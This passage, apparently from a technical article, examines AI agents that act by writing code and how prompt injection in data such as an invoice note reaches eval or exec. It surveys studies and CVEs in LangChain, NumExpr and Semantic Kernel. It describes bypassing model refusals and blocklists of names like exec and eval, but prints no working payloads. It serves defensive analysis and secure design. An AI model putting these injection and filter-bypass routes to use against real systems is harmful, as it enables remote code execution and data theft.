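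But developers can make a great many artificial examples, and Wang and colleagues already saw signs in 2024 that commercial models had trained on JSON. A model can also know Python well and still send it in a form that doesn't run. In the main test by Patel and colleagues, on 309 tasks from a standard benchmark called BFCL, code matched or beat JSON for 11 of the 14 models. The other three did much worse with it:

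| Model | JSON | Code |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o | 81.9% | 55.0% |
| GPT-4.1 | 81.9% | 62.1% |
| GPT-5.4-mini | 79.3% | 55.0% |
| Average of the other 11 | 78.0% | 82.3% |
| Average of all 14 | 78.6% | 77.0% |

The three models often wrote a backslash and the letter n instead of a line break, and Python rejected longer scripts that contained them. A framework might be able to correct this formatting error automatically. Patel and colleagues link the error to older generations of models, but that doesn't fit well with GPT-5.4-mini, which dates from March 2026. GPT-5 and GPT-5-nano came out seven months earlier, and both did better with code. Release date is an unreliable guide, so developers have to test the model they plan to use.

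The largest gains in the study partly reflect the newest OpenAI models' poor results with JSON on this benchmark. GPT-5.6-Sol and GPT-5.6-Terra scored 72.2% and 73.5% with JSON, well below GPT-4o, a model from 2024. With code, each scored 10.6 points higher, reaching 82.8% and 84.1%.

Familiarity gives code a small advantage with most current models. The argument for code actions doesn't depend on that advantage, since a model equally good at both formats could still write a loop only in code.

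### Generality

A set of tools covers only what its developer thought of. A model that writes Python can use any library available to it. Wang and colleagues show an agent downloading a table, training a statistical model on it and plotting the results without a purpose-built tool for any of these steps.

One objection is that a specialised tool may do a common job better than general code. *When Does Restricting a Coding Agent to execute_code Help?* (Yang, Yu and Desell, 2026) tested this with two commercial programming agents, Anthropic's Claude Code and OpenAI's Codex, which normally have separate tools for reading, searching and editing files and for running commands. The researchers replaced these with a single tool that ran code, then compared the cost with that of the cheapest set-up that kept more tools. They used 93 computing tasks and 100 tasks that involved fixing problems in existing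 software.

| Agent and task | Change in cost with code only | Statistically significant? |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Code, computing | −24.6% | Yes |
| Codex, computing | −6.7% | No |
| Claude Code, fixing software | +14.4% | No |
| Codex, fixing software | −19.9% | Yes |

Success rates differed by less than three percentage points in every case. When fixing software, Claude Code wrote about 40% more text, partly because it had to express every edit as a script instead of making one call to an editing tool. The agents could run code in all the set-ups, so the experiment doesn't compare code with JSON calls alone. It does support the premise by showing that one general tool could replace a whole collection without making the agents noticeably less capable, but it gives no sign that they became more capable.

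The more serious objection is that if a language lets the model do useful things the developer didn't foresee, it also lets the model do harmful ones. How much harm the program can do depends on where it runs.

### Where the program runs

The five premises support using a programming language as the format for an agent's actions, but not passing the program to `exec` inside the application. Loops and variables work just as well in a separate interpreter, and models are familiar with Python wherever it runs. The agent saves model calls because a program can carry out several steps, which it can do in any environment that lets it call the tools.

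The evidence for code actions also comes largely from programs that ran outside the application. Patel and colleagues ran theirs in a separate process, and Rai used one with limits on its resources. A separate process is a weak barrier, because it normally runs with the same user permissions as the application, but these experiments show that the benefits don't depend on sharing the application's memory. Cloudflare's Code Mode isolates programs much more strongly. It runs each one in its own small JavaScript environment, with no internet access and no passwords or keys, and the program can reach the outside world only through the functions that represent its tools. Varda and Pai say this is so fast that it is "almost as if you were just eval()ing the code directly".

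Generality is the strongest argument for `exec`, though not a sufficient one. Code running inside the application can use every library installed there and every open connection, such as a live link to the accounting database. But a developer can install the same libraries in a container. The isolated code doesn't need the database connection either if the application lets it call a function for each operation the task requires. These functions, which run in the application, are called host functions.

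Saving work is the other possible justification. Anthropic admits that a secure environment needs isolation, resource limits and monitoring, and that direct tool calls avoid this work. That may be a good reason to choose tool calls for a simple application, but not to choose `exec`, which avoids the work only by leaving out the protection. Isolation limits what a bad program can touch, although Felendler and colleagues found attacks that succeeded without breaking out of the sandbox. In an isolated environment, the invoice script can make the two calls it needs, `list_invoices` and `send_email`, without being able to read the logins for the accounting database and the mail server.

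## How injected text reaches an interpreter, and how often it has been found

If the framework instead runs the invoice script inside the application, an outsider can get at those logins without access to the machine. The outsider needs to get a sentence into the prompt, and the framework has to pass the model's reply to an interpreter. Researchers have found many popular frameworks where this is possible. It is much harder to establish how many working applications are vulnerable and how often anyone attacks them.

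### From a customer's note to the interpreter

In the version of the invoice agent where ordinary code fetches the invoices, the model only has to list the amounts that qualify. A customer can add a note to an invoice, worded as an instruction to the model. The framework pastes the note into the prompt with the rest of the record. The model may follow the note and write code where the developer expected "1200, 800". The framework then passes the reply to `eval`, which runs the code with all the application's rights.

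When injected text reaches an interpreter, the model and the interpreter are both working as designed. Microsoft (2026) made this point after its researchers found a flaw in Semantic Kernel, which pasted a search value from the model into an expression and evaluated it. The researchers blamed the trust that the framework and its tools place in the model's output. In *From Prompt Injection to Web Exploitation*, Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian (2026) similarly argue that in web applications the model usually carries an attacker's influence to an existing weakness.

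Programs that look for injection flaws traditionally trace data from a source, where outside text enters, to a sink, a function that can do damage with it. *TaintP2X*, by He, Wang and colleagues, adapts this method by treating the model's reply as a source. Their program ignores replies to prompts that the developer wrote in full, because no outsider can influence those replies. It also ignores a path from source to sink if the application adequately checks the text along the way.

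In the invoice agent, the source is the model's list of amounts and the sink is `eval`. Replacing `eval` with `int` would break the path between them. The customer's note could still make the model list the wrong amounts, but it could no longer cause code to run.

That check works because the developer knows what a proper reply looks like. A similar check is much harder to write when the framework runs model output as code on purpose, because useful and hostile replies are both Python programs.

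### Why telling the model to refuse is not enough

A developer can add a line to the prompt telling the model to ignore instructions in invoices and never write harmful code. This takes little effort and may stop crude attempts, but the model may still follow the customer's note because the new line is only more text in the same prompt.

David C calls language models "inherently confusable" deputies. A confused deputy is a program that a less privileged user can trick into misusing its privileges. Because no complete fix exists for language models, David C suggests they may be the wrong choice for an application that can't tolerate the remaining risk.

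Even a model that nearly always refuses offers little protection against a persistent attacker. If it refuses 99% of attempts and each attempt is independent, the chance that at least one of 100 attempts succeeds is 1 − 0.99¹⁰⁰, or about 63%. Real attempts aren't independent, and an attacker who learns from each refusal could do better. But repeated failures may reveal the attacker, which is why David C recommends logging failed tool calls.

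The model may also lack the information it needs to refuse correctly. A data-frame agent often needs to read a file for legitimate work, and the code looks the same whether the bookkeeper's request or a stranger's note prompted it.

Refusal also depends on which model the application uses. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian built a test application and tried to make its agent send web requests it shouldn't, using five scenarios and seven models. Susceptibility varied substantially between models. They didn't test code execution, but the result suggests that a developer who relies on refusals could make an application less safe by switching models.

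A dependable safeguard therefore has to run after the model replies, in ordinary code that gives the same result every time. Microsoft advises developers to treat every tool input that the model can influence as if an attacker had written it.

### LLMSmith's search of 11 frameworks

The first systematic search for these flaws covered framework versions from 2023 and 2024. In *Demystifying RCE Vulnerabilities in LLM-Integrated Apps*, Liu, Deng and colleagues (2024) built LLMSmith, a program that reads a framework's source code without running it. LLMSmith starts from a dangerous function such as `exec`, searches for files that mention it, and identifies which functions in those files call it. It then traces their callers until it reaches a function that application developers use directly. In LangChain, it traced `exec` through the Python tool to the function that creates a data-frame agent.

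LLMSmith found 51 chains in the 11 frameworks in under a minute. PyCG, an existing program that maps all the calls in a project, found 13 and failed to finish within an hour on four of the frameworks, including LangChain. To gain that speed, LLMSmith skips checking whether an outsider's text can travel along a chain. The researchers checked that by hand and found that 44 of the 51 could run arbitrary code. The other seven included Auto-GPT's two chains, which ended in a container separate from the host system.

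The search found 20 vulnerabilities in ten of the frameworks. Nineteen allowed remote code execution and one allowed an attacker to read and write files. The frameworks' developers confirmed 17 of them. The team received credit for 13 CVE identifiers, but these don't match the vulnerabilities one to one. Three LangChain functions share an identifier, while one function in PandasAI, a library for asking questions about tables, has three. Three of the 20 vulnerabilities didn't depend on a model's reply, since an attacker could trigger them with a file or a direct request to the server.

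Maintainers of eight frameworks answered the team's reports within a day or two, but fixes often took much longer. LlamaIndex, a framework for connecting models to data, has two entries, and one is a way around the fix for the other.

### From frameworks to applications

A framework flaw matters only if applications expose it, so Liu and colleagues also tested 51 public web applications. They found 24 by searching GitHub for code that called any of six functions they suspected or knew to be vulnerable. They found the other 27 through app directories and social networks, and couldn't see the source code of most of them. Sixteen of the 51 allowed remote code execution, and one allowed SQL injection. In 14 cases the researchers could take lasting control of the server.

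Attacks succeeded on 58.3% of the applications in the first group and 11.1% of those in the second. The team attributes the difference to having the source code, which helps an attacker find vulnerabilities. But the choice of applications probably mattered too, because every application in the first group used a risky function, while nine in the second couldn't run code at all.

Few of the 34 applications that withstood the tests did so because of good security:

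| Why the attack failed | Applications |
|---|---|
| The application was broken | 13 |
| It couldn't run code | 10 |
| The cause was unclear | 6 |
| It restricted what users could ask | 3 |
| It protected the server from the code | 2 |

The two protected applications ran the model's code in the user's browser, so it never reached the server.

Some applications also returned made-up output for code they hadn't run. To rule this out, the researchers set calculations too difficult for a model to guess. Twenty applications passed this test, and 16 in the full sample allowed remote code execution, so most applications that ran model-written code were probably vulnerable.

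The models' refusals gave little protection in these tests. Seven of the 16 vulnerable applications ran the researchers' code after a plain request. In another seven, the model's instructions or safety training blocked the request at first, but the researchers bypassed them. In the remaining two, the researchers had to bypass restrictions on the code itself. PandasAI's long prompt template sometimes unintentionally kept the model from following an injected request, but the researchers overcame this too.

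Many of the applications were experiments from a period of hasty development, so the results may not describe those of 2026. Later work by a different team suggests that the problem outlasted that period. In *Make Agent Defeat Agent*, Liu, Zhang and colleagues (2025) tested 20 widely used open-source agent applications and found 34 new high-risk vulnerabilities, including code injection, in 14 of them.

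In a broader search, He et al. ran TaintP2X on 4,772 open-source repositories and found 101 suspect paths in 75 of them (1.6%). Of these paths, 74 led to functions that run code or system commands. The true number could be higher, because TaintP2X found only 27 of 35 known flaws in an earlier test, or lower, because developers had confirmed only seven of the new findings. The gap between 14 of 20 applications and 75 of 4,772 repositories probably reflects what each team searched more than any change in security.

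### How often the model is part of the flaw

Public databases list thousands of vulnerabilities in AI software, but most don't involve a model's output. For example, a program might load a malicious file before any model has run. In *Towards Demystifying and Repairing LLM-in-the-Loop Vulnerabilities* (2026), Ma, Rong and colleagues set out to separate the two kinds. They took 230 open-source components from huntr, a programme that pays people to report flaws in AI software, and collected 2,888 vulnerability records for them from three databases. Five researchers then reviewed the records by hand.

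They judged that only 116 records concerned systems built around language models, and that only 41 of those described attacks that needed a model. These 41 make up 1.4% of the whole collection. They fall into five categories:

| What the application did with the model's output | Flaws |
|---|---|
| Ran generated code or expressions | 20 |
| Ran generated database queries | 7 |
| Carried out tool actions | 7 |
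| Displayed it, for example as a web page | 4 |
| Parsed it or passed it to other functions | 3 |

The parsing flaws include one in vLLM, a program for running models, which mishandled tool calls. Running generated code with `eval` or `exec` is the most common problem in this collection and accounts for almost half of the flaws. Removing those calls would leave the rest in place.

Of the 41 flaws, 21 (51.2%) have a severity rating of critical. Such a rating doesn't measure how likely an attack is.

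*LLM-Enabled Open-Source Systems in the Wild* (Shifat, Baburaj and colleagues, 2026) examined GitHub's security advisories, which list the package versions affected by a flaw. The researchers searched for keywords related to language models and found 295 advisories published between January 2025 and January 2026. Code injection was the most common type of weakness, with 24 occurrences. Roughly a fifth had no fix when the researchers collected the advisories.

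Advisories have no field that records whether a model plays a part in the flaw. The researchers therefore excluded packages unrelated to language models, read a random sample of 100 of the remaining advisories, and sorted them into one or more categories from OWASP's list of risks. Prompt injection applied to 18, improper output handling to 12, and excessive agency (giving a model too much freedom or too many permissions) to 20. Ten advisories combined prompt injection with improper output handling, which is the closest match to the path from a customer's note to `eval`, though some of these may involve attacks that end in a web page or a system command.

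The 18% from GitHub's sample and the 1.4% from huntr's components measure different things. Huntr's list includes general machine-learning software, whereas Shifat and colleagues limited their sample to packages used with language models. Ma and colleagues also tested whether an attack needed a model at all, which doesn't correspond exactly to Shifat and colleagues' prompt injection category.

### Automated repair

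Ma and colleagues also tested whether AI agents could fix the flaws, using all 20 combinations of five repair programs and four models, including GPT-4o and GPT-5.2-Codex. A successful patch had to stop several versions of the attack without breaking the software's normal functions. The tests used prepared hostile output instead of a live model's output, so a patch couldn't pass just because the model happened to refuse.

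On average, the set-ups repaired 25.8% of the flaws that needed a model, compared with 36.6% of the other flaws in language-model software. The best of them, the OpenHands agent with GPT-5.2-Codex, repaired 22 of the 41. Newer models would probably do better, but the pattern of failures is still useful. Among failed attempts that produced a patch, 72.3% passed either the security tests or the functional tests, but not both. More often than not, the patch kept the software working and left the attack possible. (The paper gives 72.3% as a share of all generated patches, but its counts match the failed ones.)

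One of the failures involved LlamaIndex, which ran database queries written by a model. The agent's patch rejected any query containing certain dangerous words, so it also blocked harmless queries that used one of those words as a name. The developers' own fix made the database block the dangerous operation, however the model worded the query. Ma and colleagues found agents making the same mistake elsewhere, filtering the model's text when they should have restricted what it could do.

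Flaws that involved running generated code were among the easier ones to repair. Across all 20 set-ups, 34% of attempts to repair them succeeded, compared with 12% for database queries and 10% for tool actions. Ma and colleagues suggest that this is because a call to `eval` or `exec` is easy to find in the source code. Only the three parsing flaws had a higher success rate, at 55%.

### What the counts can and cannot show

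These studies show that text in a prompt can reach an interpreter in widely used software. Several teams found this independently, and developers confirmed many of the reports. The collected reports also show which mistakes recur, which helps maintainers decide where to look.

Counts of recorded flaws can't show what share of AI applications is vulnerable. Huntr pays for flaws in the components on its list, so people have more reason to search those components than others. Companies' private software hardly appears in the records. A popular open-source framework may have more recorded flaws than an obscure one because more people have examined it, even if its code is safer.

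The records don't show how applications use the vulnerable code either. The same record covers a data-frame agent on a public website and one on a single analyst's laptop, but a stranger can reach only the first.

The figures also depend on judgement. Ma and colleagues excluded records that didn't clearly show that the attack needed a model, so their count of 41 may leave out some cases. Maintainers can also disagree about what counts as a flaw in a component meant to run model-written code. One might issue an advisory, while another might say the component works as documented and the developer should have run it in a sandbox.

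An advisory records that someone found a weakness, often a researcher who reported it privately. It isn't evidence of an attack, and none of these studies counted attacks by criminals. Few incidents are publicly known, but that is weak evidence of safety because injected code may leave no trace in the application's own logs. Microsoft points out that installing a fix doesn't reveal whether someone used the flaw earlier. To find out, the owner has to search the machine's records from before the fix for signs such as unexpected programs started by the agent or unfamiliar network connections.

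## Restricted languages, and why filtered Python is not one

Many of the recorded flaws begin when a framework passes a small piece of text, such as a sum or a search condition, to an interpreter that can do far more than evaluate it. A developer can avoid this by using a restricted language, whose grammar (the rules for what counts as a program) and evaluator (the code that runs programs) cover only the operations a task needs.

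Some developers keep Python instead and try to filter out the dangerous parts before calling `eval`. This is easy to confuse with using a restricted language because both may accept the same harmless expressions. But filtered Python still allows any operation the developer has not managed to block, whereas a restricted language allows only the operations a developer has added.

### A language for sums

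Four rules are enough for a language that does arithmetic on whole numbers:

```
expression = term { ("+" | "-") term }
term       = factor { ("*" | "/") factor }
factor     = number | "(" expression ")"
number     = digit { digit }
```

Curly brackets mean that a part can appear any number of times, including none. A vertical bar separates alternatives, and quotation marks surround characters that appear in the program itself.

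Suppose the model replies with `1200 + 800`. The software first splits the text into a number, a plus sign and another number. A parser then matches these pieces against the rules. An expression must start with a term, a term with a factor, and 1200 is a number and therefore a valid factor. No multiplication or division sign follows, so the first term ends there. After the plus sign the rules require another term, and 800 is one. The parser returns a tree:

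```
      +
     / \
 1200   800
```

The evaluator is a short function that walks the tree:

```python
def value(node):
    if node.kind == "number":
        return node.number
    left, right = value(node.left), value(node.right)
    if node.kind == "+":
        return left + right
    if node.kind == "-":
        return left - right
    if node.kind == "*":
        return left * right
    if node.kind == "/":
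        return left / right
    raise ValueError("unknown operation")
```

The evaluator starts at the plus sign, calls itself on each branch to get 1200 and 800, and returns 2000. Python still does the addition, but it runs the developer's line `left + right` and never the model's text.

Suppose a customer's note makes the model reply with `open("accounts.txt")`, which would open a file in Python. An expression has to start with a digit or a bracket, so the parser stops at the letter "o" and reports an error. Rewording the request wouldn't help the attacker, because the grammar has no letters, quotation marks or dots, so a program can't name a file or a function. Even if a bug in the parser let through an unexpected node, no branch of `value` opens files. The attacker can still make the model write the wrong sum.

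A developer can use Python's `ast` module instead of writing a parser. The module turns text into a tree without running it, and a function like `value` can walk that tree and reject every node it doesn't recognise. The language is restricted because the developer's own code evaluates the tree, whichever parser built it.

### What the invoice task needs beyond arithmetic

The arithmetic language can add the two amounts once something else has picked them out. To pick them out itself, a program needs the list of invoices, the fields `amount` and `days_overdue`, a comparison with 90, and a way to repeat that comparison for each invoice. The last step, sending an email, is an action rather than a calculation. Each addition makes the language more useful, but also gives an attacker more features to exploit.

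Common Expression Language (CEL) has everything on this list except the email. Google designed it for running users' code inside other programs, and Google's *CEL-Go Codelab*, a tutorial, contrasts it with the danger of calling `eval` on a user's Python. A CEL program is a single expression:

```
invoices.filter(i, i.days_overdue > 90).map(i, i.amount).sum()   // gives 2000
```

The expression keeps the overdue invoices, takes the amount from each and adds the amounts up. The `sum` function is an extension to standard CEL from Kubernetes, a system for running software across many machines, so other applications would have to supply their own.

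CEL parses an expression into a tree, checks the names in it against the variables and functions the application has declared, and then evaluates it. The invoice application would declare `invoices`, `sum` and perhaps nothing else. An expression that called `open` would fail the check because the application had not declared that function.

An application can add functions to CEL, but they must not have observable side effects because, according to the language definition, CEL doesn't guarantee the order in which it evaluates the parts of an expression. Ordinary code therefore has to take the 2,000 and send the email. This suits the invoice task well, since the developer chooses the recipient and a customer's note can't change it.

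Starlark allows actions too. Google's engineers created it, under the name Skylark, for Bazel, a tool that builds software from source code. They kept Python's syntax so that their existing files would still work, according to Bazel's *design of skylark* (2017), and blocked access to files, the network and the clock so that the same code would always give the same result. They wanted repeatable builds, but the same restrictions are useful against hostile code. The invoice task looks like this:

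```python
def email_overdue():
    total = 0
    for i in list_invoices():
        if i.days_overdue > 90:
            total += i.amount
    send_email("finance@example.com", "Overdue more than 90 days: " + str(total))

email_overdue()
```

This program can read invoices and send email only because the application supplies `list_invoices` and `send_email`. The Go implementation of Starlark lets such functions have side effects on the application.

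Models that write Python well should be able to write Starlark too, although the similarity can lead them to use Python features that Starlark lacks. The two-line Python script from earlier would fail because Starlark has no built-in `sum` and no f-strings, Python's notation for inserting values into text. A Python application can run Starlark through the starlark-pyo3 package, so a framework written in Python could have adopted Starlark and stayed in Python itself.

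### Programs that always end

The arithmetic evaluator always finishes because it visits each node of the tree once, and a finite text produces a finite tree. Python can't guarantee this because it is Turing complete, meaning that it can express any computation a computer can perform, including loops that never end. No method can tell for every Python program whether it will stop. Designers of restricted languages guarantee that programs finish by leaving out the constructs that allow endless repetition.

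A program that is certain to end may still take far too long. With only addition, subtraction and multiplication, a whole-number result can't have more digits than the expression contains. Adding a power operator removes that limit. In Python, for example, `9**9**9` is a number with about 370 million digits.

CEL has a similar problem with its macros, such as `filter` and `all`, which repeat an operation for each item in a list. The list is finite, so a macro always ends, but nesting macros multiplies the work. Checking a list of two items takes two steps, putting one such check inside another takes four, and 30 levels would take 2³⁰, or more than a billion. According to the language definition, nested macros can take exponential time, although Google Open Source describes CEL as running in linear time, or in proportion to the input. The definition allows applications to limit or disable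 macros.

Kubernetes evaluates CEL inside its API server, which handles requests to the whole system, so a slow expression could affect everyone. The server counts cost units as it evaluates an expression, adding one for a simple comparison and 40 for creating a list, and stops the expression if it exceeds its limit. An older version documented on pkg.go.dev allowed a million units per expression, or roughly a tenth of a second, and ten million for a whole set of rules. For some kinds of rule, the server also estimates the worst case in advance and refuses to save an expression if the estimate is too high.

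Starlark's guarantee is weaker. By default, the Go version has no `while` loops, doesn't let a function call itself, and runs `for` loops only over finite sequences. Its language definition concludes that programs can't be Turing complete with these settings. But the project's introduction to Starlark in Go warns that a program can easily use up all available time and memory, and can even hang by applying a built-in operation to a list that contains itself. The application can limit the number of steps, though a single step may be very slow, and it can't cap a program's memory from inside the interpreter. The maintainers advise anyone worried about deliberate overload to run Starlark in a separate process and let the operating system enforce the limits.

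Attackers can also target the parser. Google's *syntax*, a change to the Go implementation of Starlark, fixed a flaw that let deeply nested brackets crash the application before any program had run. Starlark's design principles, as quoted by starlark-pyo3, include the claim that "it is safe to execute untrusted code". That claim is reasonable for access to files and the network, but not for whether the application will keep running.

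| | Arithmetic language | CEL | Starlark in Go (default settings) |
|---|---|---|---|
| Can select overdue invoices | No | Yes | Yes |
| Can send the email | No | No | Yes, if the application supplies a function |
| Always ends | Yes | Yes | Usually |
| Main way to overload it | Deeply nested brackets | Nested macros | Long loops and large values |

### Filtering Python before running it

A filter for Python checks the model's text, or the tree that Python's parser builds from it, and passes the text to `eval` or `exec` if it finds nothing wrong. The filter may use a blocklist, which rejects only the listed items, or an allowlist, which accepts only the listed items. If a developer leaves an entry off an allowlist, the filter rejects legitimate code and somebody soon complains. A missing blocklist entry lets dangerous code through, and the developer may not find out until an attack.

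Blocklists work especially badly for dynamic languages such as Python, in which a program can decide which function to call while it runs. It can store a function under a new name, or assemble a function's name from pieces of text, in which case a filter that checks the code beforehand can't match the name because it doesn't exist yet. Every value is also linked to its type, and types are linked to one another, so a program can start from an empty list and reach powerful parts of the interpreter. An attacker needs only one such route that the developer failed to block, and later versions of Python can add new ones. Filters on shell commands fail for similar reasons. SC Media's *Shell injection flaw found in 10 of 11 open-source AI agents* (2026) reports a survey by the security company Adversa AI that found ways around them in nearly every agent it examined.

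### NumExpr and the hidden eval

A restricted language can be hard to tell from filtered or even unfiltered Python, as LangChain's calculator, LLMMathChain, shows. LangChain replaced the calculator's `exec` with NumExpr, a library for fast calculations on large numerical arrays. NumExpr's user guide documents a small set of operators and functions, such as `+`, `sqrt` and `sin`, and describes the library's own virtual machine for computing results. A developer reading the guide could easily conclude that NumExpr accepts only arithmetic.

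But NumExpr first passed the expression to Python's `eval`, with special objects in place of the variables, to build a tree. When Python applies `+` to these objects, they record the addition instead of performing it. This avoids writing a parser, but Python evaluates the whole string, including any part that isn't arithmetic. LangChain had in effect replaced its own call to `exec` with NumExpr's call to `eval`, which could still run Python code written by the model.

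The flaw became CVE-2023-39631. GitHub's *Langchain vulnerable to arbitrary code execution via the evaluate function* (2023), published on 1 September, rates it critical and lists two fixed versions, LangChain 0.0.308 and NumExpr 2.8.5. For LangChain, the advisory notes only that NumExpr is an optional dependency, which protects people who never install it but doesn't change how the calculator evaluates an expression.

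NumExpr 2.8.5 began checking each string against a pattern before calling `eval`. NumExpr's *Release Notes* explain that many projects seemed to be using the library to read users' input, though it had no protection for that use. The pattern rejects double underscores, colons and semicolons. It also rejects attributes (values or functions attached to an object and written after a dot), except those for the real and imaginary parts of a number.

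The pattern soon rejected legitimate expressions. On 12 September 2023, McLeod (2023, *ANN*) announced version 2.8.6, which loosened the check because it was blocking variables that pandas used internally and numbers in scientific notation. The release also let users switch the check off. Version 2.8.7 loosened the rules for both again, and version 2.9.0 fixed further problems with the check. Dots are hard for a pattern like this because a dot can be part of a number, as in 1.5, or give access to an attribute when it follows a name. A proper parser separates numbers from names first, so it doesn't confuse the two uses.

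Some calculator libraries have their own parser. The JavaScript library mathjs turns an expression into a tree and blocks access to JavaScript's `eval`. This is a much better starting point than NumExpr's. Still, mathjs' *Security* page warns that unknown vulnerabilities may remain and urges care when evaluating strangers' expressions on a server.

That caution is justified. Another JavaScript library, expr-eval, also offered a parser as a safer alternative to `eval`. The vulnerability coordination centre CERT/CC reported a flaw that let an attacker define arbitrary functions in the library's context object, which holds the names an expression can use. More than 250 packages depended on expr-eval, including a JavaScript version of LangChain, and its last release was in 2019. A small grammar gives little protection if an attacker can add functions to the context and the evaluator will call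 any function it finds there.

### PALChain's four banned names

LangChain added a filter to PALChain, its component for word problems, after the component's first CVE. According to Palo Alto Networks, the filter parsed the model's program into a syntax tree and looked for import statements and calls to `system`, `exec`, `execfile` or `eval`. If it found none, PALChain ran the program.

Researchers at Palo Alto Networks reported a way around this filter on 1 September 2023. Python can import a module through an ordinary function call as well as an import statement. The filter didn't treat that call as an import, and the function wasn't on its list of banned names. Banning `execfile`, one of the four names on the list, had no effect because Python 3 had removed that function years before LangChain existed.

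The day after the report, LangChain put a warning on the download page of its experimental package. It later fixed the flaw, CVE-2023-44467, by adding more functions and methods to the blocklist. This closed the reported route, but the filter still depended on LangChain listing every dangerous name. The first fix had already failed for that reason, and a longer list makes another failure less likely but still possible.

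Developers had trouble finding out whether they had the fix. GitLab's *CVE-2023-44467* (2023) describes versions before 0.0.306 as vulnerable, but lists only versions up to 0.0.14 as affected and gives no solution. The higher number fits the numbering of LangChain's main package at the time, so the entry probably mixes up two packages. In July 2024, the Cyber Security Agency of Singapore was still alerting users to the flaw, and its *Multiple Vulnerabilities Affecting LangChain Gen AI* (2024) gave it a severity score of 9.8 out of 10.

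An allowlist would have been practical for many of PALChain's programs. Starlark, for example, has everything the bagel and counting problems need. LangChain would have lost the ability to solve problems that need an algebra library, and some programs would have failed because the model used a Python feature that Starlark lacks.

### Semantic Kernel's search filter

Microsoft's Semantic Kernel made a related mistake in a place where the developer had no wish to run code. The framework includes a store that keeps records in memory and finds those most similar to a query. Microsoft demonstrated the flaw with an agent that looks for hotels. When a user asks for hotels in Paris, the model makes a structured tool call with "Paris" as the city. To narrow down the records before the similarity search, the framework pasted this value into a line of Python:

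```python
lambda x: x.city == 'Paris'
```

A `lambda` is a short function without a name, and this one checks whether a record's city is Paris. The framework created the function by passing its text to `eval`, then applied it to each record. As in SQL injection, a value containing a quotation mark could end the quoted text early, and Python would interpret whatever followed as code.

Semantic Kernel's developers foresaw this risk and added three checks. The text had to be a single `lambda`, it couldn't contain certain dangerous names, and it ran without Python's built-in functions. Microsoft's researchers got past all three. The first check looked only at the outer form of the text, and a `lambda` can contain hostile code. The blocklist lacked several names the researchers needed. They noticed that it also didn't cover another notation for looking things up, though they didn't need to use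 it. Removing the built-in functions made no difference, because the researchers' code started with an ordinary value and reached what it needed through Python's type system.

The fix for the flaw, CVE-2026-26030, relies mainly on allowlists:

| What the fix checks | Kind of list |
|---|---|
| Constructs, such as comparisons, arithmetic and fixed values | Allowlist |
| Functions that the filter may call | Allowlist |
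| Names standing on their own, limited to the `lambda`'s own parameter | Allowlist |
| Attributes that lead into Python's system of types | Blocklist |

The first three checks in effect define a small language inside Python. They reject any construct the developers didn't list, so some harmless searches will fail, but so will dangerous constructs the developers never considered. The blocklist is still useful as an extra layer because the filter has to allow attribute access for reading a record's fields. If Python runs the approved text, this design is still riskier than a separate evaluator, because one mistaken allowlist entry could restore access to the full language.

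MITRE's *Microsoft Semantic Kernel InMemoryVectorStore filter functionality vulnerable to remote code execution* (2026), the official record of the flaw, gives it the maximum severity score of 10. The record lists version 1.39.4 as the fix and advises anyone who can't upgrade to avoid the in-memory store in production. On 20 February 2026, a day after publication, the American cybersecurity agency CISA added an assessment that noted no known exploitation.

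For a simple search by city, the framework didn't need to evaluate any text. Ordinary code can make the same comparison:

```python
matches = [record for record in records if record.city == city]
```

Here the city stays a value whatever characters it contains, as in a parameterised database query. A filter language is worth having only if the model needs to write conditions the developer can't anticipate, such as a combination of price, distance and rating.

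### SQL, a restricted language with wide reach

SQL is a harder case because it meets the definition of a restricted language and can still do great damage. It has its own grammar, and the database is its evaluator. A model can find the overdue total with one statement:

```sql
SELECT SUM(amount) FROM invoices WHERE days_overdue > 90;   -- gives 2000
```

SQL has no general way to open files or start programs. Some databases add commands for this, but administrators can deny them to ordinary accounts. The language then confines a hostile statement to the database. But in an accounting application, the database is what most needs protection. SQL can change and delete records, and one short statement can empty the invoices table. Others could read salaries or customers' bank details if the account running them has access to those tables.

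Parameterised queries don't solve this problem, because the model writes the query itself and not only the values. A filter could accept only statements that begin with `SELECT`, the command for reading data, but this is a crude allowlist. Some databases accept several statements in one piece of text, and a `SELECT` statement can call functions that change data. A SQL parser would help with the first problem, and a list of permitted functions with the second. A filter that searches for dangerous words would be worse, as the failed repair of LlamaIndex showed.

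The database's own permissions are a more dependable control. An administrator can give the agent a read-only account, and should also limit which data it can read. Many databases support views, which are saved queries that behave like tables. A view containing only the amount and age of each invoice would be enough to calculate the overdue total, so the account wouldn't need access to anything else. If several people use the agent, each person's queries should run with that person's rights. Queries also need a time limit, because even one that only reads can keep the database busy for hours.

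A Starlark program can't open a file, but if an application gives it `list_invoices` and `send_email(to, body)`, it can email the whole list to a stranger. Making the grammar smaller wouldn't prevent this, because the invoice task requires both calls. The developer could instead replace `send_email` with `email_finance_total(total)`, which accepts only a number and always emails the finance team. An attacker could still make the agent send a wrong total, but couldn't choose who receives it or attach the invoices.

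## Structured tool calls and what a schema guarantees

An agent can use a function like `email_finance_total` without writing a program, because the model can request it with a structured tool call. The developer defines the call's format in a schema, and some model providers can force the model's output to match it. Structured calls remove the need for an interpreter, and enforcing the schema prevents many formatting errors, but a call that matches the schema can still email the wrong person.

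### One call from start to finish

The developer first describes each tool to the model. The description includes a name, an explanation in plain language and a JSON schema, which specifies the form that a piece of JSON must take. For the invoice agent's general email tool, it might look like this:

```json
{
  "name": "send_email",
  "description": "Send an email.",
  "strict": true,
  "parameters": {
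    "type": "object",
    "properties": {
      "to":   {"type": "string"},
      "body": {"type": "string"}
    },
    "required": ["to", "body"],
    "additionalProperties": false
  }
}
```

A call must include both `to` and `body` as text, and no other fields. The `strict` setting is a request for the provider to enforce these rules.

The framework sends the description along with the prompt. Once the model has read the invoices, it replies with a call:

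```json
{"name": "send_email",
 "arguments": {"to": "finance@example.com",
               "body": "Overdue more than 90 days: 2000"}}
```

The framework then parses the reply, validates it and dispatches it, meaning that it calls the matching function. In simplified Python:

```python
call = json.loads(reply)
function, schema = tools[call["name"]]
validate(call["arguments"], schema)
result = function(**call["arguments"])
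```

The first line fails if the reply isn't JSON. The second looks up the name in a table of tools that the developer registered, so a request for an unregistered function causes an error. The third checks the arguments against the schema, with `validate` standing for a library function that does this. The last line passes `to` and `body` to the developer's function as ordinary strings. If a customer's note had led the model to put Python code in the body, the finance team would receive that code as text in an email.

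The framework then adds the result to the prompt and calls the model again, a cost that code actions can reduce.

### From free text to strict schemas

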